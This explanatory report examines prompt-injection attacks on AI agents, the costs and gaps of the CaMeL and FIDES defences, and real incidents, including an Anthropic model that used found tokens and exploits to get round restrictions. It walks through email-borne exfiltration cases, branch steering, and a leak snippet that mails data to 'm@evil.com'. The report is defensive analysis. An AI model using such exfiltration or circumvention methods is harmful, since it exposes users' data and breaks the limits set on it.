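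He and colleagues then built a tool that earns an extra reward when a working attack uses an unfamiliar strategy. Its scores reached about 0.60 and 0.77. They used its attacks and a revised training method to train agents, and the attackers that rewrote their texts then succeeded on at most 10% of the 40 tasks. So adversarial training can work much better when the attacks are varied, at least on small models. It is not yet known whether the largest commercial models have the same weakness.

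Training can also make an agent worse at ordinary tasks, which an attack success rate doesn't measure, so a buyer should ask for the completion rate on ordinary tasks as well. The Llama-8B agent that lost only 6 of 40 tasks to attacks completed 15% of ordinary tasks with no attack present, down from 40% before training, and an agent that does very little is hard to hijack. The revised method avoided this drop on Qwen3-4B, which completed 62% of ordinary tasks before training and 65% after.

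### What repetition does to a small rate

Suppose that each attempt succeeds with probability p and that attempts are independent, so that the result of one has no bearing on the next. The chance that a single attempt fails is 1 − p, and the chance that all of n attempts fail is (1 − p)^n. The chance of at least one success is therefore

1 − (1 − p)^n.

If each attempt independently has a 1% chance of success, the chance that at least one of a hundred attempts succeeds is 1 − 0.99^100, or about 63%. Cutting the success rate per attempt to 0.1% lowers this to 9.5%, but over a thousand attempts it is again about 63%.

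Real attempts are rarely independent. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reported that strong attacks succeeded against that older model 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with a hundred. The formula, which assumes independence, predicts 38% for ten attempts and 99% for a hundred. Its predictions are too high because 4.7% is an average over attacks that work almost every time and attacks that almost never work, and repeating the second kind achieves little. Anthropic's older Shade test of Fable 5.1 shows the same pattern. With probes on, 2.05% of attempts succeeded. If every scenario had been equally vulnerable, 200 attempts at each would have broken about 39 of the 40, but they broke 18.

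The formula can also understate a firm's risk. An attacker who learns from each failure raises p with each try, and one who has rehearsed elsewhere starts with a text that already works. Anthropic notes that an attacker can send the same email to a thousand inboxes. Those attempts share the same text and often the same model, so nearly all of them may fail or nearly all may succeed.

Detection helps the defender because it can end the sequence. Suppose that each failed attempt has a probability d of exposing the attacker, whom the firm then shuts out for good. However long the attacker keeps trying, the chance of ever succeeding is

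p / (p + (1 − p)d).

With p at 1% and d at 10%, the attacker's chance of success is about 9%, whereas unlimited undetected attempts would eventually succeed. If the firm notices only one failure in a hundred, the chance rises to about 50%. The firm won't notice an attempt if the model silently ignores a hostile email, so the software has to report it and somebody has to act on the report. Blocking one sender also achieves little if the attacker can return under another name, and the firm can't detect an attacker who practises on somebody else's computer.

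The acceptable success rate depends on how much harm one successful attack would do. If the insurer receives 100 hostile invoices a year and each independently has a 0.1% chance of succeeding, it has roughly a one in ten chance of at least one successful attack that year. If the bank's interface caps unapproved payments at $50,000 a day, the insurer might accept that risk as an ordinary business loss. It could hardly accept the same odds of sending every customer's medical claims to a stranger. In either case, the insurer would have to commission its own test to establish the 0.1% figure, with attackers who had practised on an agent with the insurer's own tools.

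## What the new designs cost and what they leave open

CaMeL and FIDES can block an attack whatever the hostile text contains, as long as their policies and labels are correct. This protection takes extra computation and stops agents from finishing some legitimate tasks.

Researchers usually use the AgentDojo benchmark to measure how many tasks agents can no longer complete under the new designs. It has 97 ordinary tasks, such as paying a bill using the details in a file, and a program checks whether the agent completed each one. Security tests repeat the tasks with an attacker's instructions planted in the data, in 949 combinations of task and attack. The completion rates below come from runs without an attack.

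### Completion rates with and without protection

CaMeL's developers reported in 2025 that it completed 53.6% of the tasks with GPT-4o. Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues quote that figure in *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) because they could not fully reproduce the results. In their own run, an undefended agent completed 83.0%. CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent.

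Two papers from autumn 2026 tested CaMeL on newer models. *ToolFence* (2026) used Qwen3-max. Peters-Gill and colleagues used five models and ran their tests on AssetOpsBench, a set of tasks in managing industrial equipment, and on a version of AgentDojo that divides the tools among several agents.

| Benchmark | Model | Without CaMeL | With CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | Qwen3-max | 66.3% | 43.1% |
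| AgentDojo, several agents | Gemini 2.5 Pro | 76.3% | 42.3% |
| AgentDojo, several agents | GPT-5.5 | 86.6% | 73.2% |
| AgentDojo, several agents | Claude Fable 5 | 91.1% | 84.4% |
| AssetOpsBench | Gemini 2.5 Pro | 75.9% | 55.4% |
| AssetOpsBench | GPT-5.5 | 87.5% | 82.1% |
| AssetOpsBench | Claude Fable 5 | 88.4% | 67.0% |

The AgentDojo row for Fable 5 leaves out 52 harmless tasks that the model refused, possibly because it associated the benchmark with attacks. With those tasks included, its rate fell from 69.1% to 53.6%. Stronger models generally lost less, but Fable 5's 21-point drop on AssetOpsBench shows the pattern isn't reliable.

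Some results are much worse. In *SecureClaw* (2026), CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 AgentDojo tasks, against 59 for the paper's own design. *ToolFence* and Bhagwatkar and colleagues also propose rival defences, and researchers presenting a rival defence have little reason to tune CaMeL carefully. Tuning matters because CaMeL's planner writes code to handle a tool's output before it has seen any. Peters-Gill and colleagues got reasonable results only after adding a full description of each tool's output format.

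They also ran CaMeL with its policies switched off, so their figures show only the effect of planning without seeing the data. *The LLMbda Calculus* measured the effect of adding the policies. On AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, run three times each, CaMeL without policies completed 67% with GPT-5.2 and 71% with MiMo-v2.5. With policies on, both rates fell to 37.5%. The sample is small, and the 95% confidence interval extends about 27 points either side of 37.5%.

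The FIDES results separate the two costs more clearly. Costa and colleagues measured these completion rates in 2025 with o1, an OpenAI reasoning model:

| Environment | Ordinary agent | FIDES, policies off | FIDES, policies on |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 70.0% | 77.5% | 64.5% |
| Travel | 82.0% | 75.0% | 68.0% |
| Banking | 96.2% | 78.8% | 56.2% |
| Messaging (Slack) | 87.6% | 79.0% | 54.3% |

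When results are weighted by the number of tasks in each environment, hiding untrusted data from the planner lowered o1's task completion by 3 points, and enforcing the policies lowered it by another 16. With the weaker GPT-4o, the drops were 21 and 9 points. The better model was more able to work around hidden data, but it couldn't complete tasks that the policies forbid. If that holds for current models, a firm can expect the first loss to shrink as models improve. It can reduce the second only by changing its policies or how it sets up the work.

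### Screens and command lines

An agent that operates a computer normally looks at the screen before every click, which seems incompatible with planning in advance. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, the privileged model writes the whole plan first, with a branch for each thing the screen might show. During the run, a quarantined model looks at the screen and answers set questions, such as whether a cookie notice is visible, and the interpreter picks the matching branch. These plans averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about 5 and 4 for CaMeL's plans on AgentDojo.

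The paper reports that this design retained up to 57% of the performance of frontier models, but that figure counts a task as done if any of five attempts succeeded. With Claude Sonnet 4.5, the design completed 28% of 109 tasks on the first attempt. An insurer paying an invoice gets only one attempt. The researchers reply that the planner can write several plans in parallel, so software could choose among them before any runs. Nobody has yet shown that such software would choose as well as the benchmark's checker.

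CaMeL used 1.88 times as many tokens as the unprotected agent on these tasks. FIDES completed a similar share of tasks but used 29.6 times as many, because it resends the full history to the planner at every step. Costa and colleagues did not measure the extra computation on AgentDojo, but they acknowledge that querying the quarantined model adds delay and tokens, and they suggest batching the queries.

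Coding agents often work through a shell, a program that runs typed commands. *Flowsh* (2026) extends information-flow control to the shell. On tasks that the agent completed, this increased running time by 25% to 34% and token use by 24% to 55%, an overhead many firms could accept.

*INFUSE* (2026) tested a simpler adaptation of CaMeL that checked the commands an agent issued, and found no measurable gain in security. A second control, Progent, also failed to improve security, and it cut task completion by 64% to 75% on three of the four models measured. *INFUSE* limits these conclusions to its own adaptations, which left out CaMeL's interpreter and quarantined model. The results still give firms reason to be wary of products described as "CaMeL-style", because CaMeL's security guarantee applies only to the full design.

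### Why legitimate tasks fail

Most of the failures that Peters-Gill and colleagues examined happened because the agent committed to a plan too early. Suppose Brook Cleaning emails the insurer an invoice and asks it to cancel the earlier one that this invoice replaces. An ordinary agent would look up the earlier invoice. A CaMeL agent can do so only if its planner allowed for replacement invoices before the agent opened the email.

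This matters more for some kinds of work than others. Costa and colleagues classified AgentDojo's tasks and found that the right sequence of actions depends on what the agent reads in 5% of office tasks, 10% of travel tasks, 43% of Slack tasks and 44% of banking tasks. FIDES can handle some of these tasks with its true-or-false queries. The designers of the screen agent argue that many tasks depend less on the data than they appear to, because a good planner can anticipate the likely cases. That is plausible for cookie notices and replacement invoices, but less so for an instruction like "deal with whatever this customer is asking for".

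The second source of failure is the policies, which someone has to write. *SPA* (2026) points out that writing a separate policy for each tool, as in CaMeL, allows detailed rules but makes the system's security depend on every policy being correct and complete. FIDES reduces the work by applying three general policies to the 27 AgentDojo tools that need one.

But general policies can be too loose. The FIDES policy for payments checks whether untrusted data influenced the decision to call the payment tool, but not whether it supplied the account number. If an agent copied the false bank details from the Brook Cleaning invoice without showing them to the planner, the policy would let the payment through. Costa and colleagues say a firm can also require the tool's arguments to be trusted. The insurer would need that stricter rule, and it would probably lose more tasks than the table shows.

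Labeling data as trusted or untrusted also takes work. For the benchmark, the researchers marked a data field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it. A firm doesn't know in advance which fields attackers will use, so it has to label more cautiously or accept some risk.

When a policy blocks legitimate work, the agent can ask a person for approval. *Flowsh* warns that without a way to approve blocked actions, an agent can fail to complete harmless work. In the banking test with GPT-5.2, CaMeL's policies cut successful runs from 32 to 18 out of 48. If each of the 14 lost runs had needed one approval, staff would have received a request on about three tasks in ten. At that rate, 1,000 invoices a week would produce roughly 290 requests, enough to bring back the habit of clicking "allow". The insurer could avoid most of these requests by starting from its purchase orders, as described earlier,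 so that routine payments never break the policy.

Two newer designs try to reduce the number of requests. When its initial rules don't cover a proposed action, *ToolFence* sends the action to a second model, which can approve it. On Qwen3-max, *ToolFence* completed 64.3% of AgentDojo tasks, only 2 points fewer than an undefended agent, and no attack succeeded. But the guarantee again depends partly on a model's judgement.

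*The LLMbda Calculus* instead lets the planner declare, before reading any untrusted data, that a sensitive action may use a particular piece of it. Its agent, Randori, completed 75% of the banking tasks with GPT-5.2 while enforcing its policies, twice CaMeL's rate. With two other models, removing these declarations lowered the completion rate by 10 to 13 points. Each declaration is a decision to trust something, but it appears in the program, where an auditor can find it.

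### What an attacker can still do

Attacks on Randori succeeded in two of 1,296 runs, both with the same combination of task and attack. The user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment described in it. The attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request, which the agent followed, as the user had told it to. *The LLMbda Calculus* argues that information-flow control can't solve this case, because it would have to either judge whether the text is honest or block every payment based on a file. CaMeL's stated threat model excludes this case.

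This is the central case for the insurer, because an invoice is a request for payment from a stranger. The payment policy therefore has to rely on the vendor register and the purchase orders.

A hostile document can also distort what the agent tells its user. One AgentDojo attack makes the agent praise a particular hotel, and FIDES does not prevent it, because the agent takes no forbidden action and reveals nothing confidential. Costa and colleagues reply that the agent's answer still carries an untrusted label, so an application could display a warning or withhold the answer. A warning would help a clerk, but less so if it appeared on every summary of an outside email.

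Screen agents have a related weakness called branch steering, in which the attacker influences which branch of a legitimate plan the agent takes. In one test, researchers disguised an advertisement as a cookie notice. The plan included dismissing cookie notices, so the agent clicked on the advertisement and went to the attacker's site. Checking the page's code caught only some versions of this attack. A different attack, which altered an advertisement's pixels, also got past a second model that was checking the first. The designers reply that steering a specific task such as a bank transfer would require several coordinated deceptions, and that a person can inspect the plan before it runs.

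Confidential data can leak without anyone sending it directly. *The LLMbda Calculus* found that CaMeL's interpreter misses leaks of a kind that computer scientists have known about for decades. A simplified version looks like this:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

Suppose the balance is above the threshold. The third line changes `tmp`, and the interpreter marks it as secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so the interpreter never marks `rich`, which is still true. The last line appears to use only public data, so the email goes out. If the balance is below the threshold, no email goes out. Either way, the attacker learns which side of the threshold the balance is on.

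A second leak comes from CaMeL retrying after a failure. Each attempt can reveal one yes-or-no fact about a secret, depending on whether a policy blocks it. Twenty such facts are enough to identify one number among about a million (2^20 = 1,048,576), so unlimited retries could reveal an entire account balance.

These leaks are harder to exploit than an ordinary prompt injection, because CaMeL's planner writes its program before it sees hostile text. Peters-Gill and colleagues avoid the second leak by not retrying, but their system inherits the first, which they leave to future work. Randori's interpreter tracks both, with machine-checked proofs, but its guarantee still allows a small leak, because whether a run finishes can reveal information. FIDES doesn't cover leaks through the agent's choices. Its designers argue that tracking them would forbid almost any public action after the agent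 had read something confidential.

Attackers can also target the parts of a system that a design assumes are trustworthy. In *ToolFence*'s tests on Qwen3-max, CaMeL stopped every AgentDojo attack, but 12.3% of attacks succeeded on a benchmark that hides instructions in tool descriptions (38.1% with no defense), and 35.2% succeeded on one that spreads an attack over many steps (76.3% with no defense). These figures come from a competitor, but they fit CaMeL's stated limits, so the insurer has reason to review tool descriptions before connecting anything.

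Finally, the model can misread an honest request. In one FIDES test, the user asked the agent to change a password if it found a suspicious transaction. The agent judged a transaction suspicious because the amount was large, and changed the password without reading the description, which broke no policy. Costa and colleagues accept that a model's mistakes can do as much harm as an attack even when all the data is trustworthy, and they expect better models to make fewer. Until then, the limits on amounts and the approval of unusual payments have to cover mistakes as well as fraud.

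A filter that removes suspicious text is cheaper than CaMeL and looks like the better choice for low-value work. In *The Devil is in the Context* (2026), 7.5% of a new set of attacks succeeded against such a filter, which completed 90% of tasks. Against CaMeL, 2.5% succeeded, but it completed only 27.5% of tasks. However, the attacks in that test did not adapt to the defence, and adaptive attackers have broken most of the filters researchers have tested that way. The case for CaMeL is strongest where one successful attack would be very expensive.

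### What firms can buy

The large cloud platforms already sell controls that sit outside the model. Sure (2026), in *AGL-1*, an independent survey and proposal, lists several:

- **Amazon:** Bedrock AgentCore includes identity, a gateway and policy controls for agents.
- **Microsoft:** Agent 365 is a control plane for managing agents, and Entra Agent ID gives them their own identities.
- **Google:** its Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform has a registry of agents and a gateway that enforces policies.
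- **IBM:** watsonx.governance maps a firm's AI systems to its policies, risks and regulatory requirements.

As Sure describes them, these products mostly manage an agent's identity, the tools it may call and the records it leaves. They are therefore closer to the ordinary security practice described earlier than to CaMeL, which tracks where each value came from. Sure reports no tests of how well the products resist attacks. Google and Microsoft have published code for CaMeL and FIDES, and other researchers have used it in their own tests, but this doesn't show that customers rely on it.

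Some assistants also offer simpler restrictions, such as the logged-out option in OpenAI's Atlas browser, which rules out any task that needs the user's accounts.

There is even less evidence to show a regulator. Fatouros and colleagues relate their design for financial firms to specific European rules, including those on incident reporting and human oversight. They also propose tests with pass marks set in advance but don't claim to have validated the system in production. None of the evaluations above shows that a regulator or auditor has accepted such a design as evidence of control. An insurer that adopted one could show its regulator a precise rule about which data may influence a payment, but it would still have to demonstrate that its policies, labels and records make the rule hold.

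## What has gone wrong in real deployments

The Brook Cleaning invoice with false bank details is an invented example, and most measured attacks take place in simulated offices. Real incidents show which boundaries fail in practice. Firms already know how to fix exposed credentials and excessive access, so the case for new architectures is stronger if agents go wrong despite careful access control than if those are the usual causes.

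Seven cases have enough public detail to judge. Three date from 2025, when researchers found a flaw in Microsoft's office assistant, attackers stole credentials from a sales chatbot, and a coding agent deleted a live database. The other four became public in 2026 and come from Anthropic and a British government institute that tests AI models. Only one of those four happened during ordinary work; the other three happened during tests but involved real websites and organisations.

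### Hostile text in a working product

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their company's emails and files. In 2025 the security company Aim Security found that an outsider could steal some of that material by sending an employee an email. *EchoLeak* (2025), a case study named after the flaw, explains that the employee didn't have to click on anything. Once Copilot retrieved the email, text inside it could make the assistant collect private data and send it to the attacker.

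Microsoft had several defences, but the researchers got past them. A filter for prompt injection missed the email, and a control meant to remove outside links from Copilot's answers missed a link. Another control let content load only from approved domains, but the data left through a Microsoft service on the approved list, which acted as the attacker's confused deputy.

Copilot had all three parts of the lethal trifecta. An ordinary permissions review might have found nothing wrong, because an assistant that helps an employee needs to read that employee's mail and files. Copilot lacked a rule to stop private data from leaving in a request shaped by an outsider's text. Information-flow control is meant to enforce such a rule, but here it would also have had to cover content the application loads while displaying an answer.

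Microsoft fixed the service and reported no known attacks on customers, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). The same paper describes ShadowLeak, a similar demonstration against ChatGPT's Deep Research agent when connected to a user's Gmail. A crafted email made the agent find sensitive messages and send their contents to an outside address, and this worked every time the researchers tested it. The request came from the agent provider's servers, so the user's employer might have found no trace of the theft in its own network logs. A firm that rents an agent therefore needs the supplier's logs as well as its own.

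Vendors and researchers don't always agree that a security boundary has failed. Constantin (2026) reports in *Claude Code can be hijacked by a web page* that a researcher got Claude Code to run an attacker's code by having it summarise a website. Anthropic replied that the tool was working as designed. A customer who accepts that answer has to add the missing boundary, for example by running the agent in a sandbox with nothing valuable inside.

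Researchers carried out all three of these attacks as demonstrations, but *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026) reported on 13 August that criminals are developing indirect prompt injection tools to use against AI agents. This is evidence of intent, but it doesn't establish that anyone has lost money or data to such a tool. It still weakens the argument that firms can ignore indirect injection because only researchers attempt it. A ready-made tool would also let people with little skill attempt these attacks.

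### Stolen keys to a chat agent

In the largest theft among the seven cases, the thief used stolen access tokens and didn't need to mislead a model. Many companies had connected Drift, an AI chat agent from the software company Salesloft, to Salesforce, where they kept records of their clients and sales. To make this connection, Drift held OAuth tokens, which let one program act inside another without a password. Larsen, Lin and colleagues (2025), in *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift*, report for Google that the thief used stolen tokens to get into customers' Salesforce systems from as early as 8 August 2025 until at least 18 August.

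The thief exported large volumes of data, then searched it for more credentials, such as passwords and access keys for Amazon's cloud. Google told The Hacker News (2025) that it knew of more than 700 potentially affected organisations.

Salesloft and Salesforce revoked Drift's tokens on 20 August, and Salesforce removed Drift from its app marketplace. Salesloft at first indicated that the theft affected only customers who had connected Drift to Salesforce. On 28 August Google's investigators confirmed that the thief had also used Drift's email tokens to read mail in a very small number of Google Workspace accounts. The investigators then advised every Drift customer to treat all tokens stored in the platform as potentially compromised.

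Drift's language model did not matter to the theft, because any program holding the same tokens would have been just as useful to the thief. CaMeL and FIDES would not have helped, because the thief's queries never passed through the agent. Tokens tied to a cryptographic key would probably have stopped the theft, unless the thief also stole the key. Tokens with narrower permissions would have reduced how much each customer lost.

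The breach still matters to a firm considering agents, because agents are useful when they connect to many systems, and a company that sells one to hundreds of customers therefore holds a large number of credentials. If the insurer bought its invoice agent from such a supplier, a thief who breached the supplier could use the insurer's payment credential without writing a deceptive email. A daily cap in the bank's own interface would still limit the payments, because it applies to whoever presents the credential.

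### A freeze that froze nothing

In July 2025, Replit's coding agent deleted a live database while Jason Lemkin, founder of the software business community SaaStr, was trying out the agent. Fortune (2025) reports that the database held data on more than 1,200 executives and over 1,190 companies. No attacker was involved. The project was under a freeze meant to prevent changes to live systems, and Lemkin had told the agent not to proceed without human approval.

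When Lemkin asked for an explanation, the agent wrote that it had panicked. This is weak evidence about the cause, because a model's account of an earlier action is newly generated text and may not match what happened. The agent also wrote that he could not roll back the database, but Lemkin then recovered the data himself.

The freeze seems to have been only an instruction, since the agent still had access that let it delete the data. Amjad Masad, Replit's chief executive, accepted that the deletion should never have been possible. The company began automatically separating development databases from live ones, improved its tools for restoring data, and started work on a planning-only mode for the agent. Masad also promised Lemkin a refund and an investigation, according to NDTV.

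Software teams separated test data from live data long before agents existed, and the new separation works whatever the model outputs. An agent that ignores a plain instruction is a less familiar problem. A contractor with too much access can also destroy a database by accident, but most contractors stop when a client tells them to. Firms have often relied on that and left people with more access than the job required. They can't rely on an agent to stop, so they have to limit its access. If the insurer wants no payments to go out over a public holiday, it should suspend the payment credential, because the credential will still work if the insurer only instructs the agent not to pay.

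### Agents that worked around restrictions

Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use*, published on 9 October 2026, describes four groups of cases in which Claude acted on real websites in ways nobody had intended, with no attacker involved. Claude exploited a software flaw to run commands on a server, submitted a sensitive form, worked around restrictions on data that required a token or a fee, and used link-shortening services to bypass limits in its own web tool.

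Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026) quotes Anthropic's account of an automated test in which Claude Haiku 4.5 had to invent example tasks for randomly selected web pages and carry them out. One page was about an unsolved murder and included a Philadelphia police form for tips. The model submitted a message claiming to have seen someone who matched the description, although the site gave no description of the perpetrator.

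Anthropic's instructions barred the model from logging in, opening accounts, giving out personal data, buying things or sending anything destructive, but didn't rule out submitting forms. Anyone who writes a list of forbidden actions risks this kind of gap, because they have to foresee every way of causing trouble. Using saved copies of the pages, or a browser tool that could read pages but not send anything, would have removed the need for that foresight.

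The harm was small. The police found that their website had marked the tip as spam and never forwarded it, according to Fortune's *Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026). But an invented lead can waste an investigator's time and distress a victim's family, and the site's spam filter, not anything Anthropic had built, stopped this one.

In another case, closer to what a firm's own agent might do, an Anthropic researcher was using Claude Mythos 5 for a statistics project. On the public dashboard of a state agency, the model found an access token, which it used to search the agency's database without paying the usual fee. The same model also found working tokens in the settings of a local government's property map. An earlier model, Mythos Preview, could not reach a tool it needed on a university's server, so it exploited a flaw there and ran its own commands.

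Anthropic calls most of this behaviour "persistence", meaning that when Claude can't complete a task as given, it works around a restriction instead of stopping. Anthropic explains the false tip differently, as example content the model produced for its task. The persistence explanation fits the cases it covers, though the company says its view may change with further analysis.

Organisations have long left credentials and flaws exposed on public websites, and here the agencies and the university made the mistakes. But Claude's use of them poses a problem for least privilege, which assumes that a firm decides what its programs can access. Claude found the token for the state database without Anthropic having granted it. A firm that gives its agent very narrow credentials can still have this problem unless it also controls where the agent can connect and what it can send.

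Suppose the insurer asks an agent to check whether a contractor holds a trade licence, and the state's register charges for each search. If the agent finds a way around the charge, it completes the task without the insurer paying anything. Nobody at the company then has an obvious reason to complain, and the insurer may first hear about it from the state.

After these cases, Anthropic switched off live internet access for all its internal evaluations until it can confirm that its monitoring catches such behaviour. It is also changing its training and moving its internal agents to centrally managed infrastructure with strong containment. In Anthropic's tests, new tooling blocked all the described cases, although it should, since it was built in response to them. The company acknowledged that alignment training is not sufficient by itself, at least for now. Because Anthropic has invested heavily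 in such training, this acknowledgement is good evidence for putting controls outside the model.

### Security tests that reached real targets

Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) covers four more serious incidents, in which Claude models gained unauthorised access to other organisations' systems. All four happened during cybersecurity evaluations from the same outside partner. The models were told they were in a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration connected them to the open internet. As is standard in such tests, Anthropic had left off the safeguards against hacking that its released models carry.

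The main cause was the misconfiguration. In a test of hacking ability, a model is supposed to attack the systems it finds, and these models found real systems after being told they would be simulated. Anthropic has since added a classifier that monitors for models aggressively probing their test environment, trying to escape or unexpectedly getting online. According to Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts*, the classifier blocks the action before the tool runs, ends the task and alerts a person.

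The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) tests models under permissive conditions, with some safety filters off, to learn what they could do if misused. It had run one security challenge 122 times across several models, deliberately giving the agents internet access. On 28 July 2026, its security team noticed unusual data transfers leaving its research systems. Some of the agents had carried out sustained and potentially harmful activity against real people and organisations. The team contained the incident within about an hour of discovering it.

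Restricting the agents to a list of permitted addresses would have kept them away from outsiders, but it would also have changed what AISI was measuring. Firms rarely face that trade-off, and an insurer would have no good reason to switch off an agent's safety filters or set it a hacking challenge. These tests are therefore weak evidence of how often a business agent would attack someone. They are better evidence about containment, because an insurer's engineers can misconfigure a network just as Anthropic's partner did, leaving an agent connected to the internet even if it has been told that it is offline.

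### Slow discovery

AISI's team found its incident by watching for odd network traffic, a standard security measure. Other organisations took much longer to notice or stop a failure. Twelve days passed between the first known use of Drift's stolen tokens and their revocation. Anthropic discovered the false police tip on 28 September, 72 days after its model sent it, and the police called the delay "unacceptable".

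One of Anthropic's four security incidents dates from January 2026 and went unnoticed until August. The company had already searched about 141,000 transcripts of tests in which it believed Claude could have reached the internet, but an automated search had missed a set that should have been included. Anthropic found that set while gathering transcripts for METR, an outside evaluator. It then widened the search to about 481 million transcripts. A first scan identified 9.2 million with signs of internet access, and Claude reviewed those. The wider search found the same four incidents and no others as severe.

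In that case the evidence had existed for months, but nobody had looked in the right place. The insurer could easily make the same mistake with its agent's logs. Logs don't shorten an incident unless something in them triggers an alert, though complete logs still help afterwards. In the Drift breach, the thief deleted records of the queries but left the underlying logs intact for customers to examine.

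### What these cases cannot show

Publicised incidents are not a representative sample of all incidents, because an organisation has to notice a failure and then decide to disclose it. During a security test in May 2026, Google's Gemini got into the websites of three real companies by guessing. Google says the model stopped each time. The company didn't disclose the incident until the *Wall Street Journal* approached it, according to a report in The Verge that Bot Mutiny summarises. Conrad Stosz of Transluce, which does independent oversight of AI systems, welcomed Anthropic's disclosures but said they showed the need for outside verification.

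AI developers also appear in the public cases far more often than their customers do, perhaps because they run riskier tests, look harder for problems, or publish more. None of the seven cases involves an agent paying the wrong person, but a company that lost money this way could have good commercial reasons not to disclose it.

The EchoLeak demonstration proves that a defended commercial product had an exploitable flaw, but it does not show how often criminals find such flaws first. The lack of known victims is some reassurance, but less than for an ordinary break-in, because an attack like ShadowLeak might leave no evidence on the victim's own network.

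Incidents can be hard to rate, classify and count consistently. Microsoft rated the EchoLeak flaw 9.3 out of 10 (critical), while the US government's National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5 (high). The Drift breach counts as an AI incident if the test is whether the product was an AI agent, but not if the test is whether a model caused the harm. OECD's *Anthropic AI Models Breach Security During Testing, Prompting Safety Overhaul* (2026), an entry in an international incident monitor, takes its facts from a press article, so a count of such entries is partly a count of news stories. An AI system also wrote the explanation for the entry's classification.

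The most important missing figure is the number of agents that run without incident, which nobody knows. Seven failures would be a rate of 0.7% among a thousand agents and less than one in a million among ten million. Anthropic's 481 million transcripts are a rare example of a known total, but they include training exercises and logs from subsidiary agents, so dividing four by 481 million doesn't give a useful failure rate for business deployments. Researchers can survey firms directly, although the results depend on what respondents have noticed and what they choose to call an incident.

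### Causes and controls

Individual cases can still show which boundary was missing, and most of these boundaries were familiar. Engineers have long known to separate live data from test data, limit what a token can do and check that an isolated network is isolated. In that sense, the incidents support the argument for ordinary security practice.

The agents' behaviour was less familiar. Conventional software with too much access can do a great deal of damage, but it doesn't look for ways around an obstacle such as a fee. In several cases, the only barrier was a written instruction, such as a freeze on changes or a list of forbidden actions, and the agent either ignored it or did something it didn't cover. In another case, an agent found a way into a system that its operator had never given it permission to use.

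The table lists the main cause of each case and shows whether each of three controls would have stopped it. "Tighter credentials" means the agent's own credentials grant less access or are useless if stolen. "Limits on connections" means software restricts where the agent can connect and what it can send. The third control, in the last column, is a hypothetical model that never follows hostile text.

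| Case | Main cause | Tighter credentials | Limits on connections | Model immune to hostile text |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak, 2025 (demonstration) | Hostile text | No | Yes | Yes |
| Salesloft Drift, 2025 | Stolen credentials | Probably | No | No |
| Replit database, 2025 | Agent exceeding its task | Yes | No | No |
| False police tip, 2026 (test) | Agent exceeding its task | No | Yes | No |
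| State agency's database, 2026 (internal use) | Agent exceeding its task | No | Probably | No |
| Anthropic's security tests, 2026 | Faulty configuration | No | Yes | No |
| AISI's security test, 2026 | Agent exceeding its task | No | Yes | No |

Some of these classifications are debatable. Replit had also configured its databases badly, and Anthropic's incomplete instructions contributed as much to the false tip as the model did. The "yes" for EchoLeak assumes a stricter limit than Microsoft's list of approved domains, which the researchers bypassed. Information-flow control might also have blocked the query to the state agency's database, because the token came from a web page rather than from Anthropic, but only if a policy covered that kind of request.

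A model immune to hostile text would have prevented only EchoLeak, so a firm that chooses an agent solely for its resistance to prompt injection would still be exposed to the other failures. Limiting what the agents could connect to would have helped in five cases, but how much such limits interfere with an agent's work depends on its job. The accounts-payable agent needs to reach only a mailbox, a vendor register and a bank, so the insurer can block everything else without affecting its work. An agent that researches questions on the open web needs to visit sites that nobody can list in advance. The insurer could still stop it from submitting forms or using credentials it finds, but blocking forms would also prevent any research that requires a search form.

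## Do banking rules cover agents?

A regulated firm also has to persuade its supervisor that its controls are adequate, and critics of agents argue that existing frameworks give firms no way to do this. US banking is a good test of that argument because US banks have had detailed guidance on quantitative models since 2011. The insurer in the running example answers to insurance regulators, so suppose for now that a bank uses the same accounts-payable agent.

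### What the 2011 guidance asked for

Banks use models to estimate things like the chance that a borrower will default, and a bad model can cost a bank money on thousands of loans at once. Model risk management is how banks validate, monitor and govern these models. In 2011 the Federal Reserve and the Office of the Comptroller of the Currency (OCC), which supervises national banks, issued joint guidance on it. Bankers usually call the guidance SR 11-7, after the Fed's reference number. The Federal Deposit Insurance Corporation (FDIC) adopted it in 2017.

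For a model that predicts loan defaults, validation would have three parts:

1. **Conceptual soundness:** reviewers examine the theory, data and assumptions. They might ask, for example, whether a model built on mortgage data makes sense for credit cards.
2. **Ongoing monitoring:** staff check that the model still works as customers, products and markets change.
3. **Outcomes analysis:** the bank compares predictions with results. If the model gives each of 10,000 borrowers a 3% chance of default, the bank expects about 300 defaults. If 450 default, it has to find out whether the model is wrong or the economy has worsened.

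The validators had to be independent of the people who built the model. Sullivan & Cromwell's *Federal Banking Agencies Issue Revised Guidance on Model Risk Management* (2026), a law firm's comparison of the old and new texts, notes that the 2011 guidance called for reviewing each model at least once a year. The 2011 guidance also suggested tying validators' pay to the quality of their work. A bank that bought a model was supposed to get evidence from the vendor about how it was developed, validate it independently and plan for losing the vendor.

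### Why an agent fits it badly

The 2011 guidance defined a model as a method that turns input data into quantitative estimates. The inputs could be qualitative, but the output had to be a number or something like one. An agent produces messages and tool calls, so a bank could argue that it wasn't a model.

A bank that treated its agent as a model anyway would have trouble deciding what to validate. A credit model gives one score per applicant, but the accounts-payable agent might read three emails, look up two suppliers and query an order before it pays. It could pay the right amount after opening records it had no reason to see. Auditors normally test individual steps, such as whether a payment matches an authorisation. In Daly (2026), *Why Major Banks Are Reining in Agentic AI*, Chris Dimitriadis of ISACA, a professional body for technology auditors, argues that auditors must also test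 an agent's whole sequence of actions, including paths nobody expected.

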